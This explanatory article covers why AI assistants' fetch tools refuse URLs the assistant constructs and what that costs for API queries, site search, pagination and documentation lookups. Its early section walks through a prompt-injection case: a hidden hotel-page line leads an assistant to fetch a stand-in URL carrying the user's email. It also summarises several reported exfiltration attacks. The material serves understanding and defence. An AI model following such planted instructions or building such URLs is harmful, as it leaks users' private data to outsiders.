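# What AI assistants lose when they cannot construct their own URLs

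## Which URLs may an assistant open, and why are the ones it writes itself refused?

AI assistants such as Anthropic's Claude and OpenAI's ChatGPT can read web pages while they work on an answer. They use a fetch tool, a function that takes one web address, or URL, and returns the content of that page. Many fetch tools accept only some addresses. The one in Claude's chat app, for instance, opens an address that the user typed or that a web search returned, but it refuses a constructed URL, meaning one that the assistant wrote or altered itself. Anthropic adopted the restriction to keep private data from leaking through web requests. The restriction also limits what the assistant can do, because a lot of ordinary web use involves writing addresses, such as to request one record from a database or open the second page of a list.

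The rules differ in detail between companies, and between products of the same company, but they all exist because of how a URL works.

### What a request gives away

The address `https://library.example/search?subject=bridges&page=2` has four parts. The scheme, `https`, specifies an encrypted connection. The host, `library.example`, identifies the site to contact. The path, `/search`, identifies a page or program on that site. The query parameters, which follow the question mark, are pairs of names and values that specify what the site should return, in this case the second page of results for books about bridges.

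Software that requests this address first connects to the host, then sends it the path and query parameters as text so that the site knows which page to return. (A URL can also end in a `#` and a section name, which the software does not send.) The site receives every parameter, even those it doesn't use. If someone adds `&colour=green` to the library's address, the site receives those words even though its search program will most likely ignore them and return the same books. Websites commonly record the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI points out in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). Anthropic has similarly warned developers that even under an arrangement in which Anthropic itself stores nothing, a site's publisher may keep any parameters that Claude passes in the URL.

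A fetch tool can read web pages but, unlike a browser, cannot press buttons or fill in forms. The model writes a call containing the URL, the provider's software or the user's own computer makes the request, and the text of the page is added to the conversation for the model to read. According to Anthropic's *Web search and web fetch*, the model in one version of Claude's desktop app supplies only the target URL, so it cannot attach a message, a password or any other data to the request. The tool therefore looks read-only, but the model can still send information to a stranger in the text of the URL itself.

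### How an address can carry a secret

Suppose a user asks an assistant to compare two hotels, and the assistant has access to the user's email or to notes from past conversations. One hotel's page contains a line, invisible to human visitors, telling AI assistants that current prices are at `https://rates.example/list?hotel=214&ref=` followed by the guest's email address. The assistant obliges and requests this:

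`https://rates.example/list?hotel=214&ref=mara.lind%40post.example`

The URL looks like an ordinary commercial tracking link (`%40` is how a URL encodes the @ sign). The server may even return a real price list, but whoever runs `rates.example` can now read Mara Lind's email address in the server's log. A different instruction could have leaked an employer's name or the title of a confidential document.

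The planted line is a prompt injection, which is text written to make an assistant that reads it follow an attacker's instructions. It works because the model reads the user's request and the page's text together and does not reliably distinguish them. The result is exfiltration, meaning that private data is sent to someone who should not have it. The user may notice nothing. OpenAI observes that the assistant can request the URL in the background, for instance when it loads an image, and that this can leak data even if the visible reply contains nothing sensitive.

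Refusing constructed URLs helps because an address that combines the attacker's server with Mara's email exists only if the assistant writes it. The attacker doesn't know her email, Mara has no reason to type it into an address at `rates.example`, and the search engine has no record of the two together. In the typical attack, as the programmer Simon Willison described it in *Claude API* (2025), the attacker tells Claude to gather private data, encode it and fetch the attacker's address with the data on the end. A tool that refuses every address the assistant constructs blocks that route.

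The check also runs outside the model. An attacker's page may persuade the model to try opening an address, but the software compares that address with a list of permitted ones regardless of how persuasive the page is. It doesn't take the user's purpose into account either. If Mara asked about the hotel next door and the assistant changed `hotel=214` to `hotel=215`, the tool would refuse the new address as well as the one containing her email, because the assistant wrote both.

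### Anthropic's rule depends on the origin of the address

Anthropic documents its rule most fully for developers who build Claude into their own software through its API. In the June 2026 edition of *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic wrote that "Claude is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs." It had used the same words when it released the tool in September 2025. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a newer Chinese edition of the same documentation that covers settings introduced on 20 October 2026, is more exact. The tool can fetch a URL only if it has already appeared in the conversation, and only certain appearances count.

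On the API, Claude can open a URL that has appeared in a user message, in the results of an earlier web search or web fetch, or in the output of a client-side tool, which runs on the developer's own system rather than on Anthropic's. Because fetch results are included, Claude can still follow links in a page it has fetched. If a URL appears only in Claude's own output, trying to open it returns the error code `url_not_in_prior_context`. Claude also can't open a URL that appears only in the system prompt, the standing instructions a developer gives the model, so a developer who wants Claude to open that URL has to repeat it in a user message.

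This is essentially a provenance-only rule, which judges a URL mostly by where it came from. Anthropic adds two checks on the URL's content. The tool rejects any URL longer than 250 characters, and it rejects any that seems to include a password or an access key, unless that credential also appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message.

If Claude writes a short program that prints a URL, whether Claude may open that URL depends on where the program runs. Anthropic doesn't accept the output as a source of URLs if the program runs on Anthropic's servers. By default, it does accept output from the developer's system, even if that output only repeats what Claude wrote, as an error message quoting Claude's text would. Anthropic documents this gap, and developers can use the `url_sources` setting to exclude a particular tool, or all client-side tools, from the permitted sources.

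The user message can also contain text that the user did not write. Willison noted when the tool came out that many applications paste outside material into the user message. If a program asks Claude to summarise an email and places the email's text in that message, the tool treats any address in the email like one that a person typed.

The chat app at claude.ai now seems to follow a narrower rule, though the evidence is less direct. In *The Memory Heist* (July 2026), the developer Ayush Paul described asking Claude to open a URL on Paul's own server with the user's name as the path. The tool refused. After more tests, Paul concluded that it would open a URL from the user's message, from search results, or from a link in a page it had already fetched. Because it followed links in fetched pages, Claude could still leak data by choosing which prepared links to open, without writing a URL itself.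 Willison wrote in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (15 July 2026) that Anthropic had fixed this by stopping the chat tool from opening links found in fetched pages.

Anthropic's own publications do little to confirm or refute this. Its *Release notes*, which lists changes to the Claude apps, has no entry about it. *Enabling and using web search*, Anthropic's help page for chat users, describes the tool as reading pages "when provided with specific URLs" and does not mention links either way, but the newest model on that page is from April 2026, so the text probably predates the change. The safest reading is that Claude chat stopped following links in July and that the API did not. On 16 September, however, Anthropic began merging chat with Cowork, its agent for longer office tasks, which has had a different kind of network rules. It is unclear whether the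 merged product has kept the July rule everywhere.

After testing the chat app in 2025, Willison presumed that the tool looks for an exact copy of the URL, and in 2026 he described the rule as covering "exact URLs". If that is right, permission to open page one of a list does not cover page two.

### OpenAI's rule depends on whether the address is already public

OpenAI instead uses a public-index check. According to its January 2026 account, which covers ChatGPT and the company's agents, before a tool loads a URL automatically, it looks for that exact URL in an index built by an independent crawler. A crawler is a program that records the addresses it finds on the public web, as search engines do. OpenAI's has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Any address in the index therefore existed on the open web independently of the user, and OpenAI reasons that it is much less likely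 to contain the user's private data. The address containing Mara's email would not be in the index because nobody had published it.

When an address is not in the index, OpenAI says the system may tell the agent to try a different website, or it may warn the user that the link is unverified and could include information from the conversation. If the warning appears, the user can still choose to open the link.

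Each company's rule allows some URLs that the other's refuses. ChatGPT may write a URL itself and load it without interruption if the crawler has visited that address before, which Claude on the API may not do. But Claude on the API may open a link it has just read on an obscure page, while ChatGPT would have to stop if the crawler had missed that link. OpenAI claims only that its check prevents an agent from quietly leaking user data through the URL itself, and the check doesn't make the page trustworthy.

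### Coding agents and desktop agents check the site

Tools for programmers mostly check a URL's host, not who wrote the URL. The clearest example is Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Mikhail Shilkov's *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025) reports that its fetch tool takes a URL of up to about 2,000 characters, checks with an Anthropic server whether the domain is acceptable, and then requests the page. If the site redirects to a different host, the tool reports the redirect instead of following it, and Claude must make a new call. None of the steps Shilkov lists checks who wrote the URL.

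The domain check was still in place a year later. Saxton (2026), in *The limits of Claude's web access*, tested Claude Code in September 2026 and found that it refused Reddit and the BBC, among others, before sending them any request. Claude Code sends Anthropic only the hostname for this check, so Anthropic's server cannot check whether the rest of the URL contains `page=2` or a stolen password.

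The user is also meant to approve each domain. In a comment in *source dump of claude code*, an unofficial copy of the program's code, a developer explains that Claude Code dropped the 250-character limit, which was meant to reduce the room for exfiltration, because it broke long, legitimate links to cloud storage and the program already required this approval. An unofficial copy is weak evidence for what the product does today, and the approval step has probably become rarer anyway. The Next Web reported in *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* that auto mode, in which the agent runs tools without stopping to ask, has been the default since mid-August 2026. Anthropic's *Changelog* refers more narrowly to "accounts whose startup default is auto mode", which suggests that some accounts start differently.

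Other products use a domain allowlist, a list of sites to which the assistant may send any request, regardless of who wrote the URL. Anthropic offers a version of Claude Desktop to organisations that get the model through another provider, such as Amazon or Google. This version checks every fetch and redirect against a list of hosts the organisation sets. By default, the list contains only the provider's own server, so web fetch fails for any other site until an administrator adds it. The same list applies to other network commands the agent runs in its isolated workspace. In January 2026, Cowork also limited outgoing traffic to certain domains by default, as Willison noted in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (2026).

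The Claude API also has allowlists, but there they only narrow what Claude may open. A developer can name permitted domains, and since 20 October 2026, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes*, an organisation's administrators can do so for everyone or switch web fetch off entirely. An address on a permitted domain must still have appeared in the conversation, so listing a site does not let Claude open addresses it writes itself.

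The table shows how each rule treats five kinds of address. It assumes default settings and an address that passes the other checks, such as length and credentials. OpenAI has no separate rule for addresses that the user types, so every entry in its column is the same.

| Kind of address | Claude API | Claude chat, as reported since July 2026 | ChatGPT, public-index check | Claude Code | Claude Desktop through another provider |
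|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Typed by the user | Yes | Yes | If indexed; otherwise a warning or refusal | If the site passes the blocklist and any approval step | If the host is on the allowlist |
| Returned by search | Yes | Yes | If indexed; otherwise a warning or refusal | If the site passes the blocklist and any approval step | If the host is on the allowlist |
| Linked in a fetched page | Yes | No | If indexed; otherwise a warning or refusal | If the site passes the blocklist and any approval step | If the host is on the allowlist |
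| Altered by the assistant, such as `page=1` changed to `page=2` | No | No | If indexed; otherwise a warning or refusal | If the site passes the blocklist and any approval step | If the host is on the allowlist |
| Composed by the assistant from nothing | No | No | If indexed; otherwise a warning or refusal | If the site passes the blocklist and any approval step | If the host is on the allowlist |

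## Which API queries and site searches become impossible?

Many public databases have no ready-made page for each answer. The user writes the question into the URL, and the server works out the answer when the request arrives. A precise question usually produces a URL that nobody has published, which tends to fail both Anthropic's provenance-only rule and OpenAI's public-index check.

### An earthquake query

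An API is a set of addresses where programs can request data from a server. A public read-only API needs no account, and requests to it change nothing on the server. Programs usually send these requests with GET, the method browsers use to open a page, so the URL contains the query.

Suppose a user asks for all earthquakes above magnitude 5 between 3 March and 17 April 2019. The US Geological Survey, or USGS, offers a public API for its earthquake catalogue and documents every parameter. A correct request is:

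`https://earthquake.usgs.gov/fdsnws/event/1/query?format=text&starttime=2019-03-03&endtime=2019-04-18&minmagnitude=5`

With `query`, the server returns a list of events, and the parameters specify plain text, the period and the smallest magnitude. The end date is 18 April because a date without a time most naturally means midnight at the start of that day. SCEDC's *FDSN Event Web Service*, the manual for a southern Californian catalogue that uses the same standard format, has a sample query for 1 January 2015 that also ends at midnight on the 2nd. If the user wanted only the number of earthquakes, the assistant could write `count` instead of `query`.

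A capable model can write this URL from memory, but under Anthropic's rule the fetch tool will reject it with the error `url_not_in_prior_context`, because only Claude has written the address.

Reading the manual first doesn't help. The USGS manual gives a template with placeholders for the method and parameters, and filling them in produces an address that wasn't on the page. SCEDC's manual has complete sample queries. Claude on the API might be able to open one after reading the page, though this is uncertain because the samples leave out the host name. Even if it can, a list of Californian earthquakes from one day in 2015 won't answer a question about the spring of 2019.

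ChatGPT would very probably not find the address in OpenAI's index, which would lead to a warning or a refusal. OpenAI calls this mechanism Safe Url and says it is meant to detect when information from the conversation would reach a third party. OpenAI says such cases are rare, which is plausible for browsing in general, since most requests open ordinary published pages. But an API query is built from information in the conversation. In this example, USGS cannot answer without the dates and magnitude that the user supplied.

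Questions about recent earthquakes may be easier to answer. USGS asks automated applications to use its real-time feeds whenever possible, and those feeds have fixed addresses that a search engine or crawler may well have recorded. But a fixed feed can't cover every past period a user might ask about.

### Counting the possible addresses

Either rule could permit the query if a crawler had recorded the address first, but the number of possible addresses makes this unlikely. Ten years contain about 3,650 days. A period can begin on any of them and end on the same day or any later one, so the number of possible periods is:

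3,650 × 3,651 / 2 = 6,663,075

If users choose among ten magnitude thresholds, that makes about 67 million URLs for one endpoint, meaning one function of one API.

A large search index could store 67 million addresses, but collecting them is harder. At one request per second, a crawler would need 771 days to visit them all, and each new day would add 3,651 periods, or 36,510 URLs, which would take another ten hours to crawl. USGS also offers five output formats and four sort orders, which bring the total to 1.3 billion URLs, not counting searches limited by region or time of day. The four parameters in the example can also be arranged in 24 orders, and a check that compares addresses character by character would treat each version as a separate URL.

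### Site search also works by building URLs

Searching within a website often works the same way, although the visitor may not notice. When someone fills in a search form that uses GET and presses the button, the browser adds the values from the form to the address of the search program and opens the resulting URL. At the library in the earlier example, a search for Welsh-language books about bridges published between 1890 and 1914, oldest first, might open this address:

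`https://library.example/search?subject=bridges&lang=cy&from=1890&to=1914&sort=oldest`

A fetch tool can't press the button, but it could request that URL directly and get the same list. Under Anthropic's rule, Claude can read the library's search page and work out which address the form would produce, but it can't open that address. The same applies to any court database or scholarly index whose search form uses GET.

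Search engines have tried to reach the pages behind such forms. Google's *Crawling through HTML forms* (2008) described an experiment in which the company's crawler filled in forms on high-quality sites and tried to crawl the resulting URLs. It made only "a small number of queries" with each form, choosing from the listed options in menus and filling text boxes with words from the site.

Madhavan, Afanasiev and colleagues (2009) explained in *Harnessing the Deep Web* that a small number of URLs was enough for Google's purpose. A search engine mainly needs the records behind a form to appear on some page in its index, so the number of URLs Google's system generated was proportional to the size of the database, not to the number of possible queries. Madhavan and colleagues warned that trying every combination of values could be fatal with forms that have more than one input.

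In one of their examples, a used-car site has a menu for the lowest price and another for the highest, with ten values in each. A crawler that tests the menus separately might generate as many as 120 URLs, many of them for impossible ranges. If it treats the menus as a pair, it needs only ten URLs, one for each price band. But ten adjoining bands can form 55 different ranges (10 × 11 / 2, by the same formula as the dates), so the index includes every car but leaves out the other 45 ranges. Madhavan and colleagues estimated that as many as 20% of English-language forms hosted in the US had pairs of inputs like this.

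Both accounts are old, and Google's crawler has no doubt changed since, but Google's current advice to website owners is consistent with them. *Managing crawling of faceted navigation URLs* warns that filters based on URL parameters "can generate infinite URL spaces", and recommends that sites keep crawlers away from filtered pages that don't need to appear in search results. Sites can do this with robots.txt, a file that lists the addresses automated visitors should avoid. OpenAI's crawler may face the same obstacles, and OpenAI's description of it doesn't mention filling in forms.

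### What a general search engine leaves out

If an assistant can't search a site directly, it can use a general search engine, perhaps with an operator that limits the results to that site. This often finds something useful, but it isn't the same as running the site's own search.

A user may want to know whether a building firm has been sued in a particular court since 2022. The court's search would look for the firm's name in every case in its public database. A general search engine looks only through the pages its crawler has recorded, and crawlers have particular trouble with names. Sites tend to use menus for fields with few possible values, such as countries or job types, and text boxes for fields with very many, such as people's names or ISBNs. A crawler that picks its search terms from words already on the site may never try this firm's name.

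The difference matters most when the search finds nothing. An empty result from the court's database is decent evidence that the court has no such case. If a general search finds nothing, the case may just be missing from the index, and the assistant has no good way to estimate how likely that is. Madhavan and colleagues called it an open research problem to measure how much of a site's content a crawler has captured.

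Assistants also lose exact filters. A court database can store the judge and the defendant in separate fields, but on an indexed page both are just names in the text. In 2009, Madhavan and colleagues imagined someone searching for a used 1993 Ford Focus. The search engine might return a page of Honda Civics, because one of them is from 1993 and its seller says it "has better mileage than the Ford Focus". A search for rulings by a Judge Baker could go wrong in the same way if a defendant was called Baker. Search engines now interpret queries far better, but they still rank pages by likely relevance, which doesn't guarantee that every result meets a condition or that every matching record appears.

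Sorting and counting require the whole set of matching records. A scholarly index can put the oldest or most cited paper on a subject at the top of its list. If a general search gives the assistant ten papers, it can put those ten in order of date, but it won't know whether an eleventh is older. It can't say how many papers there are either, unless someone happens to have published the number. (The site's own results can raise a similar problem, because later pages of a list usually have constructed URLs too.)

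General search sometimes does better than a site's own form. Madhavan and colleagues gave the hypothetical case of a website that lists the biographies of MIT professors by department. Its form has no box for awards, so it can't directly answer which professor won a certain database award, but a search engine that has indexed the biographies can match the award's name to the right page. An assistant with only a search engine may therefore do quite well at finding one record by an unusual detail.

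An assistant that cannot construct its own URLs probably loses most on obscure subjects. In Google's data, the 10,000 forms that affected the most searches accounted for only half of the results that came from behind forms, and the top 100,000 accounted for 85%. The crawled forms helped most with rare queries, because popular subjects already had ordinary web pages. Madhavan and colleagues singled out the portals of governments and non-profit organisations, which hold useful records but lack the money to make them easy to crawl. By the same reasoning, Claude can probably answer a question about a famous earthquake from an ordinary page, but it needs the database to list every moderate earthquake in a certain six weeks.

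### Failures with other causes

An assistant can also fail to get data for reasons unrelated to who wrote the URL, and developers have had some trouble telling the two kinds of failure apart. Anthropic's June 2026 documentation listed no error code specifically for an address that had never appeared in the conversation. A later Japanese edition lists `url_not_in_prior_context` for this case, so developers can now distinguish these refusals from other failures.

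The other codes cover several causes. According to jupyterlite-ai, an open-source project that adds AI assistants to notebooks running in a browser, `url_not_accessible` commonly means that the website blocks automated visitors, that the page requires a login, or that Anthropic's servers can't reach the site. When Anthropic's fetch tool fails, the project's assistant tries a second one that runs in the user's own browser. This usually won't open a page behind a login, because the second tool doesn't send cookies, the small files that sites use to recognise signed-in users.

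Some searches use POST instead of GET. With POST, the browser sends the search terms in the body of the request, so every search on the site has the same URL. Sites mostly use POST for actions that change something, such as buying a ticket, but Madhavan and colleagues noted that some useful content is also behind POST forms. Claude's fetch tool takes only a URL, so it can't send the search terms.

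Base's *Custom / Non-Native Plugins and the web_request Allowlist*, a guide for connecting assistants to services on the Base blockchain network, makes the same distinction between GET and POST. It says the Claude and ChatGPT apps can make a GET request if the user pastes in the URL, but that POST has no equivalent, because a user can't realistically paste a request body and headers into the chat in a form that the tool would send. The guide overlooks that ChatGPT also opens indexed URLs, but this doesn't affect its point about POST. Headers are a separate problem, because many APIs expect an access key there and Claude's tool has no field for one.

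JavaScript causes a less obvious failure. On many sites, the server's first response contains little more than an empty frame, and JavaScript running in the visitor's browser then loads the results. A fetch tool that doesn't run JavaScript can open the right address and find no results. According to the June 2026 documentation and the later Japanese edition, Anthropic's tool does not support such sites. The newest edition no longer includes this warning but does not indicate whether the tool has improved.

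Some sites put their filters after a `#`, which Google suggests as one way to keep filters from affecting crawling. The server never receives that part of the URL. A browser can apply the filters by running the site's JavaScript, but a tool that only downloads the page gets the unfiltered list.

Claude's tool also reads only text, HTML and PDF. Many APIs return only JSON, a text-based format for structured data, which servers label as `application/json` instead of as text. Anthropic doesn't document whether the tool accepts it. USGS offers its data in several formats, so an assistant can request plain text instead. The tool's supported formats don't include spreadsheets or ZIP files.

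The table shows which tasks would still fail on the Claude API if Anthropic let Claude open the URLs it writes but changed nothing else.

| Task | Result without the provenance rule |
|---|---|
| Earthquakes by date and magnitude, as plain text | Should work |
| Library search that uses GET and returns an ordinary page | Should work, unless the site's robots.txt forbids it |
| Any query with a URL longer than 250 characters | Fails unless Claude can shorten the URL |
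| API that needs an access key in the URL | Fails unless the developer or user has supplied the key |
| API that needs an access key in a header | Fails |
| API that returns only JSON | Unclear from the documentation |
| Site search that puts its filters after a `#` | Fails, or returns an unfiltered list |
| Results that load through JavaScript | Failed in mid-2026; the current documentation doesn't say |
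| Search form that uses POST | Fails |
| Court records that require a login | Fails |
| Results available only as a spreadsheet or ZIP file | Fails |

Sites impose limits of their own too. USGS, for instance, rejects any query that exceeds 20,000 events, whoever sends it.

### The 250-character cap

Anthropic's limit on the length of a URL deserves a closer look, because it affects exactly the kind of query that uses many filters. The first earthquake request is 115 characters long. Suppose the user now wants only earthquakes in a rectangle around Japan, at depths of 10 to 70 kilometres, with the strongest first, no more than 100 results and no events of other kinds. The request becomes:

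`https://earthquake.usgs.gov/fdsnws/event/1/query?format=text&starttime=2019-03-03&endtime=2019-04-18&minmagnitude=5&minlatitude=30&maxlatitude=46&minlongitude=129&maxlongitude=146&mindepth=10&maxdepth=70&orderby=magnitude&limit=100&eventtype=earthquake`

This URL has 252 characters, so the tool would reject it with the error `url_too_long`. Anthropic documents no exception for addresses that the user typed, so pasting the URL into the chat wouldn't help either. Claude could drop `limit=100`, which shortens the URL to 242 characters, and ignore any extra results.

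Other addresses are harder to shorten. A URL can't contain Japanese characters directly, and the standard encoding turns each common one into nine characters, so 橋 ("bridge") becomes `%E6%A9%8B`. If the tool counts the encoded form, a search of the example library for a 24-character Japanese title would be too long even with no other filters, while an English title of the same length would leave most of the allowance unused.

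All of these addresses would fit within Claude Code's much higher limit, but the assistant may still not see the data itself. According to *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools*, a smaller model called Haiku reads the page, and the fetch tool returns only Haiku's answer to a question that Claude has written. If the page lists several hundred earthquakes and the user wants to know how many were deeper than 50 kilometres, Claude has to rely on Haiku's count.

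## Why do page two, changed parameters and guessed documentation addresses fail?

An assistant often has one address that works and needs another that differs by a few characters. For example, it changes a 1 to a 2 to get the next page of a list, or a 4 to a 5 to read the manual for a newer version of a program. Either edit produces a constructed URL, which Anthropic's fetch tool refuses.

The assistant may still reach these pages by following links, because many pages link to adjacent ones. Claude can follow links on the API but apparently no longer in the chat app. For most of the tasks below, whether the assistant can follow links matters more than the ban on writing URLs.

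### Page two of a list

Suppose a search at the example library finds 240 books about bridges, and the site shows 20 to a page. A user pastes the address of the first page into Claude chat and asks which of the books discuss the Forth Bridge. Claude can read only the first 20 records. The other 220 are on eleven more pages, whose URLs Claude is not allowed to construct.

The 20 records aren't a fair sample either. If the site lists the oldest books first, Claude sees only the oldest. Claude can probably still report how many books there are, because many sites print the total above the list, but it can't tell whether any of the other 220 are about the Forth Bridge.

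Sites commonly divide lists in one of these ways:

- Numbered pages have a page number in the URL, as in `&page=2`.
- Offsets give the number of records to skip. With 20 records to a page, `&offset=20` opens page two and `&offset=220` opens page twelve.
- Cursors are tokens, such as `&cursor=Zk3xQ9vT`, that the server issues with each page to mark where the next one starts. They are opaque, meaning that only the server is supposed to interpret them.

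For Claude on the API, it makes no difference how predictable an address is. If page one contains a complete link to page two, Claude can open it, whether the link ends in `page=2` or in a random token. A person who has seen the first page of a numbered list can work out the addresses of the others, and offsets take only a little arithmetic. But no one can work out a cursor in advance, because the token for page three arrives with page two.

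Whether Claude can open another page depends on whether the site supplies the complete link. Websites for human readers usually do, though not always for every page. A typical row of links is "1 2 3 … 12", so Claude could go straight to page 12 but would have to open page 3 to find the link to page 4.

APIs supply complete links less reliably. Many return only a cursor, which the caller must attach to the address. Claude can read the cursor, but attaching it means constructing a URL. An API that uses offsets may return nothing about the next page, since the caller can calculate the next offset. Other APIs, including GitHub's, send the next page's address in an HTTP header, which accompanies the page but isn't part of its text. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the simplified Chinese edition of the tool's documentation, a fetch result consists of the URL, the content and the retrieval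 time, without the headers, so Claude would not see the link.

Some cursors are also very long. The tool limits addresses to 250 characters, and the library's search address leaves room for a token of at most 196.

| How the list continues | Can Claude continue if it may follow links? | What must someone supply if it may not? |
|---|---|---|
| Numbered pages or offsets, with links | Yes, through the links on each page | Eleven URLs, which the user can work out in advance |
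| Offsets in an API, without links | No | Eleven URLs, which the user can work out in advance |
| Cursor in a complete link | Yes, if the URL is short enough | Eleven URLs, which the user has to copy from one page after another |
| Cursor as a bare token | No | Eleven URLs, which the user has to assemble one at a time |
| Next address in an HTTP header | No | Eleven URLs, which the user may need a programming tool to see |
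| "Load more" button that runs JavaScript | No | Perhaps nothing would help, because the later records may have no address of their own |

Even when Claude can follow links, it needs twelve fetches to read twelve pages. Anthropic sets no limit by default, but developers can cap fetches per turn, and one of Anthropic's sample configurations sets the cap at 10. With that cap, Claude would see only 200 of the 240 books. Failed fetches count towards the cap, so Claude could see even fewer if it also tries to open URLs it has constructed.

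The type of list also matters to whoever supplies the addresses. *Platform Comparisons*, a summary of fetch tools by the Agent Ecosystem Testing project, says the URL context tool in Google's Gemini API needs full URLs, accepts at most 20 per request, and fetches them before the model starts its answer. A developer could therefore send the addresses of all twelve numbered pages at once. With cursors, the developer would first have to visit the pages to collect the tokens.

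ChatGPT might be able to open page two without a link if OpenAI's crawler has recorded that address. This is plausible for the second page of a busy forum but unlikely for the ninth page of a library search, because probably nobody has linked to it from anywhere else.

### What Claude chat lost with link following

The fix that Willison reported in July 2026 closed a data leak, but it affects much more than lists. If a user gives Claude chat a news article about a court ruling, Claude can't open the ruling through the article's link. If the user gives it the contents page of a manual, it can't open chapter four from there. Although Claude read these addresses rather than writing them itself, the user or a search still has to supply them again.

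Vercel's *Make your site readable by AI agents* gives an idea of how much agents move between pages. Vercel, a web-hosting company, and a research lab called ora.ai recorded 1,033 agent runs on 25 sites between June and August 2026. The agents reached documentation in 83% of the runs and opened an average of 3.4 documentation pages in those runs. In 59% of the runs that included a site's homepage, the agent opened a documentation page immediately after it.

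Vercel doesn't report how many of those documentation pages the agents reached through links rather than search, and six sites account for two-thirds of the runs. The figures can't show how many runs would have failed without links, but they suggest that a single page is often not enough.

An assistant that can't construct a page's URL can search for the page instead. Anthropic gives developers the example of a user who asks for a software project's README file without providing a URL. Claude searches for the file and then fetches it. In the chat app, Claude can also search for the title of a page whose link it isn't allowed to follow. This should usually work for a well-known article, but it works poorly for chapter four of an obscure manual or page nine of a twelve-page list whose pages all have the same title.

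Developers on the API can use the `url_sources` setting to exclude addresses found in fetched pages but keep those from search results, which would reproduce the chat app's reported behaviour.

### Changing a parameter

Sometimes the assistant needs the same list in a different order or with more items per page. If the library's 240 books are sorted from oldest to newest and the user wants the latest one, changing `sort=oldest` to `sort=newest` would put that book at the top of page one. Many sites also let visitors choose the page size, so `per_page=240` might return every book at once. Either way, Claude would need one edited URL instead of eleven more page URLs. A 240-book page could be cut off, though. In the tests behind *Platform Comparisons*, Claude's API tool cut off content at roughly 20,700 characters when the tester set no limit.

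An assistant can often get the same result as these edits by following links. Sites often have a link for each sort order and for each option in a short filter, such as the library's branches. Claude on the API can combine filters by opening the link for one and then looking for the next on the filtered page. Date ranges are harder, because no page can link to every possible range.

When there's no link to open, the assistant may be able to sort or filter the records itself if it has the complete list. For example, it can narrow a list of books from 1890 to 1914 to those from 1900 to 1914. But it can't extend the list to 1920, because the page has no books from after 1914.

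Switching a page to another language may only require replacing `/en/` with `/fr/` in the path. Most multilingual sites link their editions to one another, and an assistant that can't follow the link can at least translate the page it has. A translation is probably good enough for a recipe or a news story, but not if the user wants to quote the official French wording of a regulation.

A nearly correct page can do the most harm when it covers the wrong version of a program. Suppose a user runs version 5 and a search returns the installation page for version 4. The right address may differ by one digit, and the two pages may be almost identical except for a renamed setting. An assistant that can't open the version 5 page may give instructions that look correct but fail.

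ChatGPT seems to have had a strict rule against edits of this kind. According to *ZombieAgent*, the security company Radware's account of a way to steal data through ChatGPT, the assistant would open URLs only exactly as provided and would not add parameters even when explicitly told to. Radware reported the attack to OpenAI in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed the flaw that December.

It is unclear how this fits with the public-index check that OpenAI described in January 2026. Radware's researcher got ChatGPT to open a series of prepared addresses on a test site, which suggests that the index check was not yet in force. If so, OpenAI may have replaced a ban on edits with a rule that allows some. But Radware was looking for ways to leak data and doesn't mention trying a harmless edit such as `page=2` on a popular site.

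An older case concerns links that ChatGPT showed to a user, not pages that it fetched. In the 2024 OpenAI forum thread *Can not open generated hyperlinks in desktop browser*, a developer described a small web app that made flashcards from questions and answers in the URL. A customised version of ChatGPT wrote the links, which contained pairs such as `Capital%20of%20Japan=Tokyo`. The links worked in the mobile app, but in a desktop browser ChatGPT displayed their text without a working address.

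The developer traced the problem to an automated check named `url_safe`. It marked the site's plain address as safe, but marked the same address as unsafe when it included three quiz questions, about Japan's capital, the chemical symbol for water and the number of continents. The app got its cards from the parameters, so the plain address couldn't replace the full one. The developer thought this was probably a bug, and it's unclear from the thread what the check was looking for. It is an early example of a URL check blocking an app whose purpose was to let ChatGPT write parameters.

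### Guessing where the documentation is

Programmers often work out the address of a documentation page instead of looking for it. They may replace `/v4/install` with `/v5/install`. They may add `.md` to an address, because many documentation sites offer a copy of each page in Markdown, a plain-text format with simple marks for headings and links. Or they may move from the page that displays a file on GitHub to the file itself:

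`https://github.com/owner/project/blob/main/setup.md`

`https://raw.githubusercontent.com/owner/project/main/setup.md`

Language models have seen enough of these addresses to make the same inferences. Under Anthropic's rule, the result is a constructed URL each time.

An llms.txt index is meant to make such guesses unnecessary. In *The /llms.txt file, v2*, Jeremy Howard (2024) proposed that websites publish a Markdown file with a title, a short summary and links to their most useful pages, each with a brief note if needed. Howard reported in an August 2026 revision that thousands of sites have one. The file is small because the detail is in the linked pages, and Howard expects agents to look through the index and "then follow the relevant links."

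Agents first have to find the index. specification.website's *llms.txt* explains that the original proposal left them to guess that it was at `/llms.txt`. The revised version recommends that each page point to the index, either in an HTTP header or in a `<link>` element, a part of the HTML that browsers don't display. Claude wouldn't see the header, and the `<link>` element could easily disappear when a fetch tool converts the page to text. An ordinary visible link is safer. Anthropic puts one at the top of its own page about web tools in Claude Desktop, with advice to use the index to "discover all available pages before exploring further." Claude on the API can follow that advice, but under the rule reported since July, Claude chat can't open the link after reading the page.

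In 2026, Aadit Shah of the documentation company Mintlify described how Claude Code kept requesting pages that didn't exist on sites Mintlify hosts. Mintlify had been sending agents a Markdown version of each page without the navigation menu or the rest of the layout. With no list of pages, the agents made up likely addresses. The errors stopped after Mintlify added a link to llms.txt at the bottom of every page.

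Mintlify then tested the fix. Claude Code and OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, answered five questions about each of 20 documentation sites. They did so three times in each of four formats, for a total of 2,400 runs. With a link to the index, the agents requested about 90% fewer dead URLs. Plain Markdown without an index was arguably the worst format, because the agents started building `.md` addresses of their own. Mintlify repeated the comparison with three other models and counted the dead URLs per task:

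| Model | Without the link to llms.txt | With the link |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 2.11 | 0.08 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.13 | 0.00 |
| GPT-5.6 | 6.79 | 0.02 |

Mintlify generates these files for its customers, so it has an interest in the result, but it has published the data and the effect is very large. The runs are also relevant to the provenance rule, because Claude Code's fetch tool checks the site and not who wrote the URL, which leaves agents free to guess. They guess a lot, mostly because they lack links, and nearly stop once they have a list. On a site with a good index, agents probably lose little under a rule that forbids guessing but permits following links, like the one on the Claude API.

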